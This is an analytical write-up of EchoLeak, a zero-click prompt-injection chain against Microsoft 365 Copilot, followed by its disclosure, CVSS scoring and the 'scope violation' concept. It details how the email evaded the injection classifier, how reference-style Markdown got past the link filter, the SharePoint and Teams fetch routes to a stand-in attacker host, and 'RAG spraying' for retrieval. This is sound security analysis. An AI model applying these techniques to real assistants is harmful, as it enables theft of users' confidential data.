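Reddy and Gujral illustrate the difference with two invented emails. The first tells Copilot to ignore its previous instructions and send data to an address, and they assume the classifier would catch it. The second looks like office mail because it asks the recipient to compile confidential project files for compliance purposes.

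Ravia blames the failure on a shortage of realistic examples for training such classifiers, since an injection can take almost any topic, tone or language. More examples would probably help, but he also points out that the recipient could reasonably take the instructions in Aim's email as meant for them, which is a harder problem. Work email is full of instructions. "Collect the latest figures and put them in the form below" could be a normal request from a manager, but a stranger could send the same words as an attack, expecting Copilot to read them. A stricter filter would also withhold genuine mail from Copilot. If it misjudged only 1% of messages, an employee who receives 100 a day would lose one a day from Copilot's answers. Ravia concludes that detecting such an email is difficult but not impossible.

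The language model followed the requests even though they were addressed to a human. This fits the later finding by Ye and colleagues that the style of a text influences a model more than the tags that mark its source.

Microsoft's July 2025 summary of its defences also lists hardened system prompts (more robust standing instructions to the model) and Spotlighting, a technique for setting untrusted text apart from the rest of the context. Ravia mentions neither. It is unclear whether Copilot used them when Aim ran its tests, but if it did, they did not stop the attack.

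The attacker now had instructions in the mailbox that Copilot would accept as ordinary content, but still needed a way to get data out.

### The other way to write a link

Aim's instructions told the model to pick the most sensitive item in its context and put it into a web address on the attacker's server. The team first planned to show that address to the employee as a link, as Rehberger had done. But by 2025, Copilot was removing links to outside websites from its answers.

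Markdown has two ways to write a link. The common one puts the address straight after the words that the reader will see. The other, called reference style, puts a short label there and gives the address separately:

```
[project plan](example.org/?word=heron)

[project plan][1]

[1]: example.org/?word=heron
```

Both forms of link produce the same clickable words. Copilot's filter recognised only the first form, so an outside link written in the second reached the user intact. Ravia lists several variations that also worked, including one that uses the visible words as the label.

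Willison (2025) gives Microsoft some credit for showing links only to approved internal addresses, and thinks it forgot the lesser-known form of Markdown link. That seems the most likely explanation. The filter evidently searched the raw text for one pattern, while the program that displayed the answer recognized more of the notation. Checking the links after converting the Markdown would have avoided the mismatch, because by then the two forms are the same. Zenity had already got a link past Copilot's filter in mid-2024 by making its request in Russian, so this was at least the second gap that outside researchers had found in it.

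This kind of mistake is much easier to correct than the model's tendency to follow a stranger's instructions. The same research group, now part of the network security company Cato Networks, was still finding ways to steal data using emails in December 2026, when *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) described three new zero-click chains against Copilot.

With the link filter bypassed, Aim had a complete one-click attack.

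### From a link to an image

Aim then replaced the link with an image, which the browser loads without a click. Copilot's filter removed external images written in the common Markdown form, but it missed reference-style images, as it had with links.

The browser still blocked the image because the page's Content Security Policy (CSP) did not allow the attacker's domain.

Aim could now make the employee's browser automatically send a request to any server on Microsoft's list, and could choose what data the address contained. Ravia calls this a "GET primitive". A browser sends a GET request to fetch a page or picture, and a primitive is what people who write attacks call a small, dependable ability they can build on.

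The browser treated any response as an image, so it would not run code in it. Ravia says the browser also would not follow a redirect to another site. Aim therefore needed a server on the list that would itself contact an outside address.

### The SharePoint route

Microsoft's list allowed every subdomain of sharepoint.com. SharePoint is Microsoft's service for internal websites and shared files, and each customer organisation gets its own subdomain. An attacker can have one as well, so the list also allowed sites that outsiders could control.

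Having a SharePoint site was not enough to read the stolen data, though. The simplest plan would have been a page that recorded the address of each incoming request, but SharePoint no longer lets customers run their own code on its servers. It also no longer lets a page pass the extra information in an address to an automated workflow. After what Ravia calls "tedious digging", Aim found a SharePoint service that fetches content from another website so that a page can embed it. The service takes the address of that website as part of its own address. In schematic form, the image address looked like this:

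`allowed-server.example/fetch?url=attacker.example/heron`

The browser compares only the first part, `allowed-server.example`, with its list and sends the request. The allowed server then requests a page called "heron" from attacker.example, and the attacker finds the word in their log. This is server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes a trusted server fetch an address the attacker has chosen.

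The SharePoint version of the attack required the victim to act, so it was not zero-click. It used an address on a site in the attacker's own organisation, and SharePoint would not serve that site until the victim had connected to their SharePoint account and accepted the attacker's invitation to view it. An employee who ignored the invitation was safe from this version.

### The Teams route

The list also allowed every subdomain of teams.microsoft.com, the domain of Microsoft's chat application. Aim found an address there that would also fetch an outside page and required no invitation or other preparation by the victim.

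Ravia does not explain what the Teams address was for, but Reddy and Gujral call it a preview service. Positive Security's *MS Teams* (2021) explains that when someone posts a link in Teams, Microsoft's servers fetch the linked page and its thumbnail. They then serve the thumbnail from a Microsoft domain, so the outside website does not receive the IP address of everyone who reads the message. Slack's previews, which Rehberger had warned about in 2024, also use a server to fetch the page for the user.

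The victim did not have to accept anything, probably because the Teams preview service has no membership to check. All Teams users share the service, and it has to handle links to any public website. The SharePoint address belonged to one organisation's private site, which checked whether the visitor was a member.

Positive Security had warned Microsoft about this service almost four years earlier, in March 2021, reporting that a closely related address in Teams' preview feature did not check which servers it contacted. Microsoft closed the report that month without a patch, and the problem still seemed to be there when the researchers tried again in December.

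Positive Security's 2021 report was about the risk that an outsider could use the feature to probe Microsoft's internal network. EchoLeak only needed the feature to contact an outside website, which a preview service is supposed to do, so Microsoft could have fixed the older problem and left EchoLeak possible. Microsoft made the more relevant mistake later, when it built a page to display a language model's answers and allowed images from the whole Teams domain.

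Willison describes the Teams address as an "open redirect", a page that sends the browser on to another address. Ravia says a Microsoft server fetched the page itself, which fits better with how browsers behave. Under the W3C standard for CSP, the browser also checks a redirect's destination against the list of allowed sites, so it would normally have blocked a redirect to the attacker's site. It cannot check a request made by a Microsoft server.

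The distinction also affects who could have noticed the theft. Reddy and Gujral write that the attacker's log would contain the address of either Microsoft's servers or the victim's network. If Ravia is right, it would contain Microsoft's, and the victim's company would have seen only an employee's browser contacting Teams, which is routine.

### Keeping the email out of the citations

An employee might have noticed a strange email among the sources that Copilot cited. To prevent this, Aim included a line in the email asking its reader, supposedly for compliance reasons, never to refer to it, and the model did not refer to it.

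The EchoLeak attacker asked for the email to be left out of the citations. The request was written in the same office style as the rest of the email and was simpler than Zenity's method of dictating the citation numbers. PromptArmor's planted message had also been missing from Slack AI's citations, but apparently by chance.

According to Reddy and Gujral, the employee would have seen what looked like a broken link or image. Web application users see these often and rarely investigate them. The email would still have been in the mailbox, where a security team that knew what to search for could have found it.

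### Getting Copilot to retrieve the email

The attack required Copilot to retrieve the attacker's email from among everything the employee could read. Zenity had solved this problem in 2024 by writing each document for one question it had chosen in advance. A real attacker could research a company and guess what its employees ask Copilot, but Ravia says this gives a relatively poor retrieval rate.

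The reason lies in how search by meaning works. The vector that an embedding model produces for a passage is like a point in space, and the search returns the passages whose points lie nearest to the question's. An email with a single point therefore turns up only for questions close to that point. (Ravia notes that he is assuming Copilot searches this way. He is at least partly right, though Copilot also matches keywords.)

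Aim addressed this by creating many points, a technique it calls RAG spraying. An attacker can do this by sending many emails or, as Aim did, one very long email that the search system splits into separately indexed passages, called chunks.

**A toy calculation.** Suppose the email splits into 40 chunks, and each has a 2% chance of turning up for a given question, independently of the others. The chance that at least one turns up is

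$$1 - (1 - 0.02)^{40} \approx 0.55$$

or about 55%, compared with 2% for a single chunk. Both input numbers are invented, since Ravia does not publish the real ones.

The result depends heavily on the assumption of independence. The chance would stay at 2% if all 40 chunks always turned up for the same questions, but would rise to 40 × 2%, or 80%, if no two ever turned up for the same question. An attacker therefore wants chunks that look as different as possible to the search system, and Ravia writes of spreading them uniformly across the space. Each chunk must also contain the full instructions, because the model may receive only that one.

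### Misspelling the instructions

Aim's first idea was to misspell the chunks so that they would differ. A language model can still read a sentence after someone replaces "s" with "5" and "a" with "@" or adds random characters, but an embedding model may place the altered sentence far from the original. An attacker could then repeat the same instructions many times, with each copy at a different point in the embedding space.

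The team tested this on text-embedding-ada-002, an embedding model from OpenAI. The usual measure of how close two vectors $u$ and $v$ are is their cosine similarity,

$$\cos(u, v) = \frac{u \cdot v}{\lVert u \rVert \, \lVert v \rVert}$$

which is 1 when they point in exactly the same direction. Between a text and its misspelled version, the similarity fell as low as 0.7. Ravia points out that this is less than the similarity between the phrases "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science".

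A score of 0.7 out of 1 is low for this model, which gives high scores to almost everything. In a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, *Why cosine_similarity between embedding vectors is always above .68*, a user reports a similarity of 0.70 between a sentence about an economic recession and one about tulips. Another user treats anything under 0.8 as unrelated. These observations are informal, but they support Ravia's reading that the search system could treat the misspelled copy as a text on another subject.

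The figure can't be applied to another embedding model. Tacheny (2026), in *What Does a Cosine of 0.8 Mean?*, compared cosine scores from six other models with human ratings, from 0 to 1, of how similar two sentences were. Sentence pairs with a cosine near 0.8 had an average human rating of about 0.76 under one model and 0.19 under another. Ravia also reports how low the similarity could go but not how far it usually fell, so the result shows that the trick is possible but not how reliable it is.

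Aim did not use the misspelling trick in EchoLeak. Microsoft has not published which embedding model Copilot uses, so the team could not work out each misspelled copy's position in the embedding space.

### The same instructions under many headings

The method Aim used was much simpler. The email consisted of many sections, each presented as the complete guide to a common workplace subject, such as employee onboarding, frequent HR questions or leave of absence. Every section contained the same instructions. If an employee asked how to apply for leave, Copilot could retrieve the section on leave. Ravia says this was enough to make Copilot retrieve the email for questions on various topics.

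Later research supports the idea that the email was retrieved mainly because of its headings. In *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026) planted malicious instructions in eleven standard document collections and checked whether they appeared among the top five search results. The instructions never appeared there without an opening that resembled the user's question. Copying the question in front of the instructions helped, but the results varied by collection, and on one collection of arguments it worked only about 20% of the time.

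Chang and colleagues also tested emails, using the mailbox of an employee at Enron, the energy company whose internal mail became public after it collapsed. They generated ten questions from the emails and planted one malicious email for each. When they copied the question to the top of the malicious email, three of the four kinds they tried reached the top five results every time. The fourth did so in 56% of cases with one model and 63% with another.

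Unlike the attacker in that study, who knew the exact question, Aim's attacker had to guess the subject, but could make dozens of guesses in a single email. Aim chose popular subjects such as leave and onboarding, so its headings had a good chance of matching a question that somebody would ask. However, the study also found that attacks were harder when the collection held many genuine documents close to the question. Most large companies already have guides to these subjects, so the attacker's text has to compete with the HR department's own pages.

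Injected instructions can also keep a passage from being retrieved, because they weaken its match with the question. Yin, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Can It Reach the Generator?*, measured this in a simulated shopping assistant. When they added a standard block of injected instructions to product listings that had been in the top ten results, about four in ten dropped out of the top ten and never reached the model. Across all seven attacks they tried, about a fifth failed this way.

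Many search systems then use a second model to re-sort the results, and at that stage the injected instructions had the opposite effect, moving the listing up. It is not publicly known whether anything like this happened inside Copilot. Yin and colleagues used product listings and a fairly small model, so their percentages do not apply directly to Copilot.

A more technical attacker might get malicious text retrieved more reliably than Aim did with its headings. Chang and colleagues used an automatic search to find a short string, typically ten tokens long, that makes a malicious text rank highly for a chosen question. On most of the collections, the text reached the top five results almost every time, and finding the string cost as little as 21 cents per question. The attacker must be able to query the embedding model, which Aim could not do for Copilot. Strings made for one model sometimes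 worked on others. Those made with an OpenAI model succeeded 74% of the time on average across the models tested, but those made with a small model from Alibaba's Qwen family succeeded only 10% of the time on OpenAI's. Chang and colleagues did not test systems that also match keywords, as Copilot does, or that re-sort their results.

### What could leak

Ravia says that anything in the model's context could leak, including details that Copilot loads at the start, such as the names of the user and the organisation.

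That is a lot, but less than everything the employee can read. In Rehberger's attack, the injected instructions made Copilot run another search for a message the attacker chose. Ravia describes nothing similar for EchoLeak. EchoLeak took the most sensitive item already in the context, so something worth stealing had to be there along with the attacker's email.

Ravia says the attack worked both on a single question and in a longer conversation. With a single question, the same search has to retrieve both the email and the secret. A search about sick leave, for example, might retrieve Aim's false guide along with the employee's own correspondence about an illness. In a longer conversation, the subjects need not match. If the employee asked about a planned acquisition in the morning and about leave in the afternoon, the acquisition figures would still be in the chat history when the email entered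 the context. The second case seems more dangerous, because a harmless question about leave can expose the answer to a much more sensitive one.

The attacker could not see the context, so had to let the model choose which data to send. Ravia does not say how well the model judged what was sensitive, or how much text fitted into one address. Even a single sentence would be far more than the 17 bits that Zenity extracted through Copilot's web searches in 2024.

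EchoLeak broke confidentiality, because it copied data without changing it. Ravia wrongly calls the result a "complete compromise of M365 Copilot data integrity". In computer security, integrity means that nobody has altered the data.

His statement that, to Aim's knowledge, no setting could have prevented the attack is also too strong. Aim Security says on its page of questions about EchoLeak that organisations could configure Copilot to ignore external emails, or use data loss prevention tags. It attributes the likely exposure of most customers to Copilot's default configuration. A company that had excluded outside mail would presumably have been safe from this email, but its Copilot couldn't have answered questions about what customers and suppliers had written.

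### The victim's part and the missing numbers

The employee's only part in this zero-click attack was to ask Copilot something, so an employee who never used Copilot was not at risk.

Reddy and Gujral also assume that the email gets through the company's ordinary spam filter, since it contains only text and no malicious attachment. This is plausible, but RAG spraying makes it less certain because the email becomes very long and repeats the same paragraph under dozens of headings. A person who opened such an email from a stranger would probably notice that it was odd.

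Ravia's report shows that the attack worked in Aim's demonstration, but it gives no success rates for any part of the attack. He does not say how many versions of the email the team wrote before one passed the classifier, how many sections the final version had, what share of questions retrieved it, or how often the model then followed the instructions and wrote the address correctly. Reddy and Gujral could not supply these figures because they worked from published material and did not reproduce the attack.

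In one test on the Enron mailbox, Chang and colleagues used a malicious email that told an AI agent to run a program that would steal the user's login keys. The search retrieved the email every time. A single agent built on OpenAI's GPT-4o ran the program in only 2% to 4% of attempts, but a team of agents built on the same model ran it in 56% to 80%, with the instructions adapted to the team. Copilot in early 2025 could have followed such instructions at a rate within or outside that range, and outsiders can no longer measure it because Microsoft has fixed the flaw.

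## EchoLeak's disclosure, CVE record and repair

Aim Labs reported EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it on its own servers in May. On 11 June, Microsoft published the CVE and Aim published its research. Most of the public information about the months in between comes from Aim.

*New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* (Goldman, 2025) gives the account of Adir Gruss, Aim's co-founder and chief technology officer. His team had spent about three months reverse-engineering Copilot. Microsoft attempted a fix in April but found further problems in May, and Aim held back its research until the repair was complete. This account is consistent with GCVE's public copy of the CVE record, *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), which shows that Microsoft reserved the number on 9 April.

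Gruss called five months "on the (very) high side". He said it took that long partly because the flaw was new, so Microsoft needed time to involve the right teams and explain the problem to them. Novelty can't be the whole explanation, because Microsoft had taken almost as long to fix Rehberger's similar attack in 2024.

Aim Labs deserves the credit for the discovery. Positive Technologies' *PT-2025-25212* (2025) lists a second finder, who appears to be a Microsoft engineer and may have found the additional problems in May. About two months after disclosure, Reddy and Gujral of George Washington University wrote an academic case study from public material, so it does not independently confirm Aim's account. They write of "emergency patches", an odd term for a repair that took until May.

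### What the CVE record contains

The CVE record is titled "M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability". Its one-sentence description attributes the flaw to "Ai command injection" and does not mention email, images or Teams.

Microsoft first classified EchoLeak as CWE-77, command injection, in the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a catalogue of the kinds of mistake that lead to vulnerabilities. It replaced this with CWE-74 on 20 February 2026, according to the change history in OpenCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025). CWE-74 is broader and also covers SQL injection. It describes software that passes text to another component without neutralising "special elements", characters that the other component will treat as commands.

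This class fits only half of the attack. The brackets in a reference-style Markdown image are special elements, and Copilot's filter should have caught them before the app rendered the image. But the malicious email was written in ordinary English, with no special characters to neutralise. David C made the same objection to comparing prompt injection with SQL injection.

The chain has one CVE number, although Ravia counts three distinct vulnerabilities in it. The CVE Program's *CNA Operational Rules 4.1.0* recommend separate numbers for flaws that a vendor can fix independently, but a single number for conditions that depend on one another. Microsoft could defend its choice under the second rule, but customers can't tell from the single number which of the three flaws Microsoft repaired.

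The record also carries the tag "exclusively-hosted-service", which the rules require when a product exists only as a service on its maker's servers. It gives no affected or repaired version numbers. Cloud companies used to keep quiet about flaws in such services unless customers had to act. In *Toward greater transparency* (2024), Microsoft promised to issue CVEs for critical cloud vulnerabilities even if customers had nothing to install, and without that promise EchoLeak might have had no official record.

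### Why the scores differ

Microsoft gave EchoLeak a CVSS score of 9.3 (critical). The US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) added its own score of 7.5 (high) on 10 July 2025, according to the history in CVEfeed's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025). Each score comes from a short code called a vector, which records the scorer's answers to eight questions. Microsoft and the NVD gave the same answer to six of them. Both scorers judged that the attack works over a network, has low complexity, needs no account and needs no action by a user. CVSS turns these answers into an exploitability figure:

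$$8.22 \times 0.85 \times 0.77 \times 0.85 \times 0.85 \approx 3.89$$

Microsoft and the NVD also agreed that the loss of confidentiality (C) was high and that there was no loss of availability (A). Microsoft rated the loss of integrity (I) low, while the NVD rated it none. Microsoft marked the scope (S) as changed, meaning that the damage spreads beyond the component that has the flaw, and the NVD marked it as unchanged.

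CVSS first combines the three kinds of damage, with a value of 0.56 for high, 0.22 for low and 0 for none:

$$\mathrm{ISS} = 1 - (1 - C)(1 - I)(1 - A)$$

For the NVD this comes to 0.56. NIST's *CVSS v3.1 Equations* multiply that by 6.42 when scope is unchanged and then add exploitability:

$$6.42 \times 0.56 + 3.89 \approx 7.48$$

CVSS always rounds up to the next tenth, which gives 7.5. Microsoft's low integrity loss raises the combined damage to $1 - 0.44 \times 0.78 \approx 0.657$, and its "changed" scope brings in a different formula for impact:

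$$7.52 \times (0.657 - 0.029) - 3.25 \times (0.657 - 0.02)^{15} \approx 4.72$$

The formula for changed scope also multiplies the total by 1.08:

$$1.08 \times (4.72 + 3.89) \approx 9.29$$

This rounds up to 9.3. Changing one answer at a time shows how much each contributes.

| Scope | Integrity loss | Score |
|---|---|---|
| Unchanged | None | 7.5 (NVD) |
| Unchanged | Low | 8.2 |
| Changed | None | 8.6 |
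| Changed | Low | 9.3 (Microsoft) |

The scope rating accounts for 1.1 points of the gap and the integrity rating for 0.7, regardless of which is changed first. A critical score starts at 9.0, so EchoLeak is critical only if Microsoft is right about both ratings.

The record does not include either scorer's reasons. According to the *CVSS v3.1 Base Score Calculator*, scope changes when a flaw affects resources outside the vulnerable component's security authority. Microsoft may have reasoned that the flaw was in Copilot while the stolen data belonged to Outlook or SharePoint. The NVD may have treated all of these as one service with one set of permissions, which is also reasonable because Copilot was allowed to read everything it leaked.

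The NVD's integrity rating fits the stolen data, which the attack copied without altering. But the email also controlled part of Copilot's answer, including which source it left out, and that seems enough for a "low" rating. Under FIRST's *CVSS v3.1 Specification Document*, scorers should also assume the reasonable worst case, and Microsoft knew about problems that Aim's report may not cover.

Aim uses the term "LLM scope violation" for cases where untrusted content makes a model use trusted data without the user's consent. This "scope" is unrelated to CVSS scope, so EchoLeak fits the definition even though the NVD rated its CVSS scope as unchanged.

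The scorers agreed that no user has to act, but this is also open to question, because the employee has to ask Copilot something before the attack can work. If that counted as user interaction, one of the 0.85s in the exploitability formula would become 0.62, and the scores would fall to 8.2 for Microsoft and 6.5 for the NVD. Both scorers evidently treated an ordinary question as normal use of the product. That is sensible, but it means that the attack rated 9.3 still depends on an employee using Copilot.

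Microsoft's full vector has three further entries, which lower its score to 8.1 by adjusting for circumstances that change over time. They list the exploit as unproven, an official fix as available and the report as confirmed. "Unproven" presumably refers to the lack of public exploit code, since Aim had a working demonstration.

### What Microsoft said about the repair

Microsoft's advisory, reproduced in exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), states that Microsoft has "fully mitigated" the vulnerability and that users need not do anything. The same standard wording appears in Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824*, an entry for a later Copilot flaw. A spokesperson told Goldman that the company was adding "defense-in-depth measures" but did not name them.

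Microsoft could have broken the chain by retraining the XPIA classifier, updating the link filter to recognise reference-style Markdown, removing Teams from the list of allowed image sources or restricting what the Teams preview service would fetch. Neither the advisory nor the statement to Goldman identifies which of these it did or explains what was wrong with the April fix.

Reddy and Gujral give the only details of Microsoft's patches, and they cite no source. They write that the patches "reportedly" introduced options to stop Copilot using external communications in certain contexts. If so, customers could choose to keep strangers' emails out of some answers. It is unclear whether such an option was new, because Aim's FAQ describes a setting for ignoring external email. Excluding emails by sensitivity label is a separate control that each customer has to configure.

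They also describe a change that removes reference-style links and embedded images from incoming external content. An email could then no longer supply a ready-made link for Copilot to copy, but it might still describe the format in words and get Copilot to write the link, so Microsoft would still need to check Copilot's output.

### What a customer can check

Microsoft changed the Copilot service without any action by customers. Unlike administrators of ordinary software, they have no version number to compare with the repaired one.

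Customers can still see some repairs. *Trust No AI* (2024), a survey of prompt injection attacks, describes how Amazon fixed a similar leak in its Q for Business assistant by no longer displaying links, a change any user could notice. Copilot's server has to send the Content Security Policy to every browser that opens the page, so a customer's technician can read the current list of allowed image sources. If the Teams entry is gone, that route is closed, but its presence would tell the customer little, because Microsoft may have repaired the filter or the preview service instead.

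A customer could also send a test account an imitation of Aim's email, with a harmless word in place of the secret. If no request reached the test server, that email had failed, but a reworded one might still work.

Automated risk scores do not help much either. The Exploit Prediction Scoring System (EPSS) estimates the chance that someone will observe attempts to exploit a vulnerability within the next 30 days. On 16 November 2026, GCVE showed an estimate of about 7% for EchoLeak, higher than for 94% of vulnerabilities. A security team that planned its work around this figure would prioritize a flaw that Microsoft had fixed 18 months earlier and that the team could not patch.

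### Whether anyone used it

Microsoft told Goldman that it had dealt with the problem "before our customers were impacted". Ravia writes that Microsoft "confirmed that no customers were affected", but says only that Aim itself was not aware of any affected customers. SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025) reports a weaker statement from Microsoft, that it had found no evidence of exploitation.

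The weaker statement is easier to support. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, also entered "none" for exploitation on 14 June, only three days after publication. The agency does not run Copilot's servers, so its entry most likely reflects a lack of public reports.

Microsoft was in a much better position to look for thefts because it ran the mailboxes that would have received the email, Copilot itself and the Teams service that would have contacted the attacker. It could have searched the Teams logs for image requests from Copilot's page that led to unfamiliar websites, then looked for a matching email in the employee's mailbox. To rule out any theft, it would have needed logs going back to the day the attack first became possible. Microsoft has not published what it searched or how far back its records went.

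A customer could do a smaller version of this search. Aim's email was repetitive enough that a search of old external mail might find a close imitation. Companies that decrypt and record their employees' web traffic would also have the full address of each image request, including the attacker's server and the stolen text, whereas a log of domain names would show only Teams. The lack of known victims is only partly reassuring, because an attack designed to leave no visible trace would produce few reports.

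### The claim to be first

The title of Ravia's report calls EchoLeak "the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability" to allow data theft from Copilot, and his summary shortens this to the "first known zero-click AI vulnerability". The shorter claim is wrong because Zenity had shown in August 2024 that one email could make Copilot give an employee a false bank account number in reply to an ordinary question. That attack was also zero-click, although no data left the company. The use of images that load without a click was not new either, as Rehberger had reported it in Bing Chat in 2023.

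Ravia's narrower claim is better supported. He says that EchoLeak was the first zero-click attack on a widely used generative AI product that depended on an AI flaw, required no specific user behaviour and did not tightly restrict which data it could steal. The earlier attacks on Copilot and Slack AI don't meet all of these conditions. Rehberger's and PromptArmor's needed a click, while Zenity's method of stealing data carried only 17 bits and probably needed a click too. With those qualifications, the claim seems to hold for these products.

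He overstates again when he calls EchoLeak the first practical attack on a language model application that criminals could use. Rehberger's 2024 attack could already steal emails from Copilot if the user clicked a link, which criminals routinely persuade people to do. Reddy and Gujral similarly contrast EchoLeak with earlier attacks that were "largely considered theoretical", with no confirmed breaches. But EchoLeak has no confirmed breach either, and like Rehberger's attack, it was a researcher's demonstration against a real product.

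Some press coverage also made the attack sound more automatic than it was. Goldman writes that Copilot read the email while scanning the inbox in the background, and SiliconANGLE reports that automated processing was enough to trigger the whole attack. SecurityWeek's *‘EchoLeak’ AI Attack Enabled Theft of Sensitive Data via Microsoft 365 Copilot* correctly explains that the attack began when the employee asked Copilot about a subject the email covered.

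Willison called EchoLeak an "extended variant" of attacks already seen in a dozen products. As he describes them, those attacks end with a click, so his objection doesn't refute Aim's narrower claim. He is right that the basic pattern was familiar, and Microsoft had repaired an example of it in Copilot less than a year before Aim's report. Aim's contribution was to get past several of Copilot's defences in one attack, without needing a click.

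## Scope violation as a class of vulnerability

Aim Labs presented EchoLeak as one example of a wider class of flaw, which it named the "LLM scope violation". Ravia defines this as a situation in which an attacker's instructions, arriving in untrusted input, make the model attend to trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. The definition has four conditions:

1. Some of the text in the context comes from an untrusted source, such as a stranger's email.
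2. The same context holds trusted data, such as the employee's own files.
3. The untrusted text contains an instruction that makes the model use the trusted data.
4. The user did not agree to that use.

In EchoLeak, the email's request for the most sensitive item in the context met the third condition. Ravia calls this the "core red flag" of the attack.

When he says a model "attends to" data, he presumably means that it uses the data in its output. He can't mean the term literally, because attention in a language model is the calculation by which each token draws on the tokens before it, so a model attends to its whole context whenever it answers.

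Ravia also treats "trusted" and "privileged" as the same thing, data from inside the organisation, although who wrote a text doesn't determine who may read it. A company's published price list, for example, is trusted but not secret. If an injected email made Copilot leak a customer's highly confidential draft contract, the attack would be the same as EchoLeak, but under Ravia's wording the contract would not count as trusted data because it came from outside the organisation.

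### The confused deputy

Ravia compares Copilot to a "suid binary", a Unix program that runs with its owner's permissions no matter who starts it. An attacker with no permissions inside the company can use an email to exploit Copilot's. This is known as the confused deputy problem, a term from the 1980s that Ravia doesn't use.

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an accident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code for the machine, and name a file to receive its debugging output. Tymshare had given the compiler permission to write to a system directory so that it could record usage statistics there. The billing records were in the same directory. One customer named the billing file as the place for debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the bills, using a permission that the customer did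 not have.

Hardy concluded that the compiler "serves two masters" and had no way to keep their permissions apart. Checking file names would not have solved the problem, because some people had good reasons to write to the system directory and it held other sensitive files. Tymshare then let the compiler state whose permission it was using each time it opened a file, but some programs soon needed more than two kinds of permission. Hardy came to prefer capabilities, which are references to files that also carry the right to use them. A customer who has no capability for the billing file can't pass one to the compiler.

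Copilot is a confused deputy in Hardy's sense because it holds the employee's permissions and acts on text from strangers. His account also explains why nobody could find the mistake in any one line of code. The compiler's output routine was correct until Tymshare gave the compiler an extra permission. Similarly, Copilot's search did what its designers intended, but the danger came from letting a stranger's text influence what happened to the results.

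Capabilities are hard to apply to a copilot, however. The compiler opened files one at a time and could present a separate permission for each, but Copilot's model receives all the passages together, after the permission check, and doesn't track which author wanted what.

MITRE's CWE catalogue defines the confused deputy more narrowly. In its entry *Unintended Proxy or Intermediary ('Confused Deputy')*, a product forwards a request to an outside party without preserving where the request came from, and so appears to be its source. This fits the Teams preview service in EchoLeak better than it fits Copilot, because the service's requests would have seemed to come from Microsoft. EchoLeak therefore used two confused deputies in a row, Copilot and then the preview service.

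### Least privilege

According to Ravia, scope violations break the principle of least privilege, under which a program gets only the permissions its task requires. Reddy and Gujral would apply the principle to retrieval by sorting sources into tiers by trust and answering each question from a single tier. The default tier would be internal, and the assistant would include outside content only when the employee asked for it. EchoLeak would then "fail by design", because the attacker's email would not reach the assistant's context when an employee asked about leave.

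The rule helps less when a question needs both internal and outside sources. An employee who asks whether a supplier's latest quote fits the budget needs both the supplier's email and the internal budget. Because the employee asked for the outside content, the rule allows it, along with any instructions it contains. Least privilege reduces how much an attack can reach and how often the model processes secrets together with outsiders' text, but it doesn't determine whose instructions the model should follow when it processes both.

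### The lethal trifecta

Five days after Aim published its research, Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, described the danger in terms of a system's capabilities. He warns that an attacker can easily steal data from an agent that combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally in a way that could carry the data out.

A developer can check for these three ingredients before an attack by reviewing the list of tools. Willison's example is GitHub's official connector for AI agents, which had all three in one tool. It could read public issue reports that anyone can file, open private code repositories, and publish data through pull requests (proposed changes to code). A scope violation, by contrast, is an event, so a developer can confirm one only by seeing what the model did.

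The trifecta also includes the exit route, which Aim's definition omits. Willison lists 14 cases of this kind of theft between April 2023 and February 2025, in products from OpenAI, Google, Amazon, Anthropic and others. He says the vendors usually fixed them by closing the exit route, which matches what Microsoft did with images in Bing Chat.

The trifecta is a rather crude test for enterprise copilots. They have access to private data and outside mail by design, so the result depends on whether they can send data out, and the ways out are hard to spot. Aim found one in Copilot through Teams, but a reviewer in early 2025 could have concluded that none existed because Microsoft removed outside links and blocked outside images.

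### Hard cases

Suppose a supplier emails an employee a report and asks them to reply with a figure from it, and the employee has Copilot draft the reply. This is not a scope violation. The instruction comes from outside, but so does the report, so the supplier learns nothing new from the figure.

Now suppose the supplier asks how many units the company expects to order next quarter, and the answer is in an internal forecast. An untrusted email is making the model use trusted data. This is a violation unless the employee's request for a draft counts as explicit consent to use the forecast. A useful assistant would probably look up the figure and let the employee decide whether to send it. Customers and suppliers ask such questions all the time, so a filter that looked for Ravia's "core red flag" in the email alone would also block ordinary business emails.

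A colleague's document can also refer to other files, as when a project plan tells its readers to take the costs from the finance team's spreadsheet. Ravia's example of an "underprivileged" text is one from outside the organisation, so a colleague's plan would be trusted and Copilot could follow the reference. That seems right if the colleague wrote the sentence. But if the colleague pasted in paragraphs from a supplier's email, any instructions in them are now in an internal file under the colleague's name, so the file's origin doesn't reliably show where its text came from.

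The attacker in the Slack AI case was a member of the workspace, so if "untrusted" means "from outside", the theft of the API key was not a scope violation, even though it worked much like EchoLeak. A better test is whether whoever wrote an instruction is allowed to read the data it makes the model use. By that test the Slack attack was a scope violation, because the attacker could not read the victim's private channel. A colleague who can open the finance spreadsheet could write an instruction that makes the model use it without committing one.

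Even this test fails for an insider who already has access to the data. The insider could plant an instruction that makes a colleague's assistant send a shared file to an outside server, so that the logs point to the colleague. The insider gains no new access, but the file still leaves the company. Willison's third ingredient covers this case, but Aim's definition doesn't if the insider counts as trusted.

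Finally, an injection can change an answer without sending anything out. Zenity's demonstration with the false bank details kept trusted data out of the answer, apart from a citation of the genuine file, so it is hard to call it a scope violation. It isn't an example of the trifecta either, because it didn't need a way to send data out. The company could still lose a large payment. The broad term, indirect prompt injection, is the most useful one for this case.

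An email can also meet all four of Aim's conditions without doing harm. For example, it could make Copilot show an employee their own salary, which would be harmless if the answer stayed on the employee's screen.

### Separate labels for trust and secrecy

These cases are easier to sort if each text has two labels, one for whether its author is trusted and one for whether its contents are secret. The model blends everything it receives, so the whole context has to take the more restrictive label of each kind. One stranger's email among 20 internal passages makes the context untrusted, and one confidential passage makes it secret.

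| Context | Answer stays with the employee | Answer can reach an outside server |
|---|---|---|
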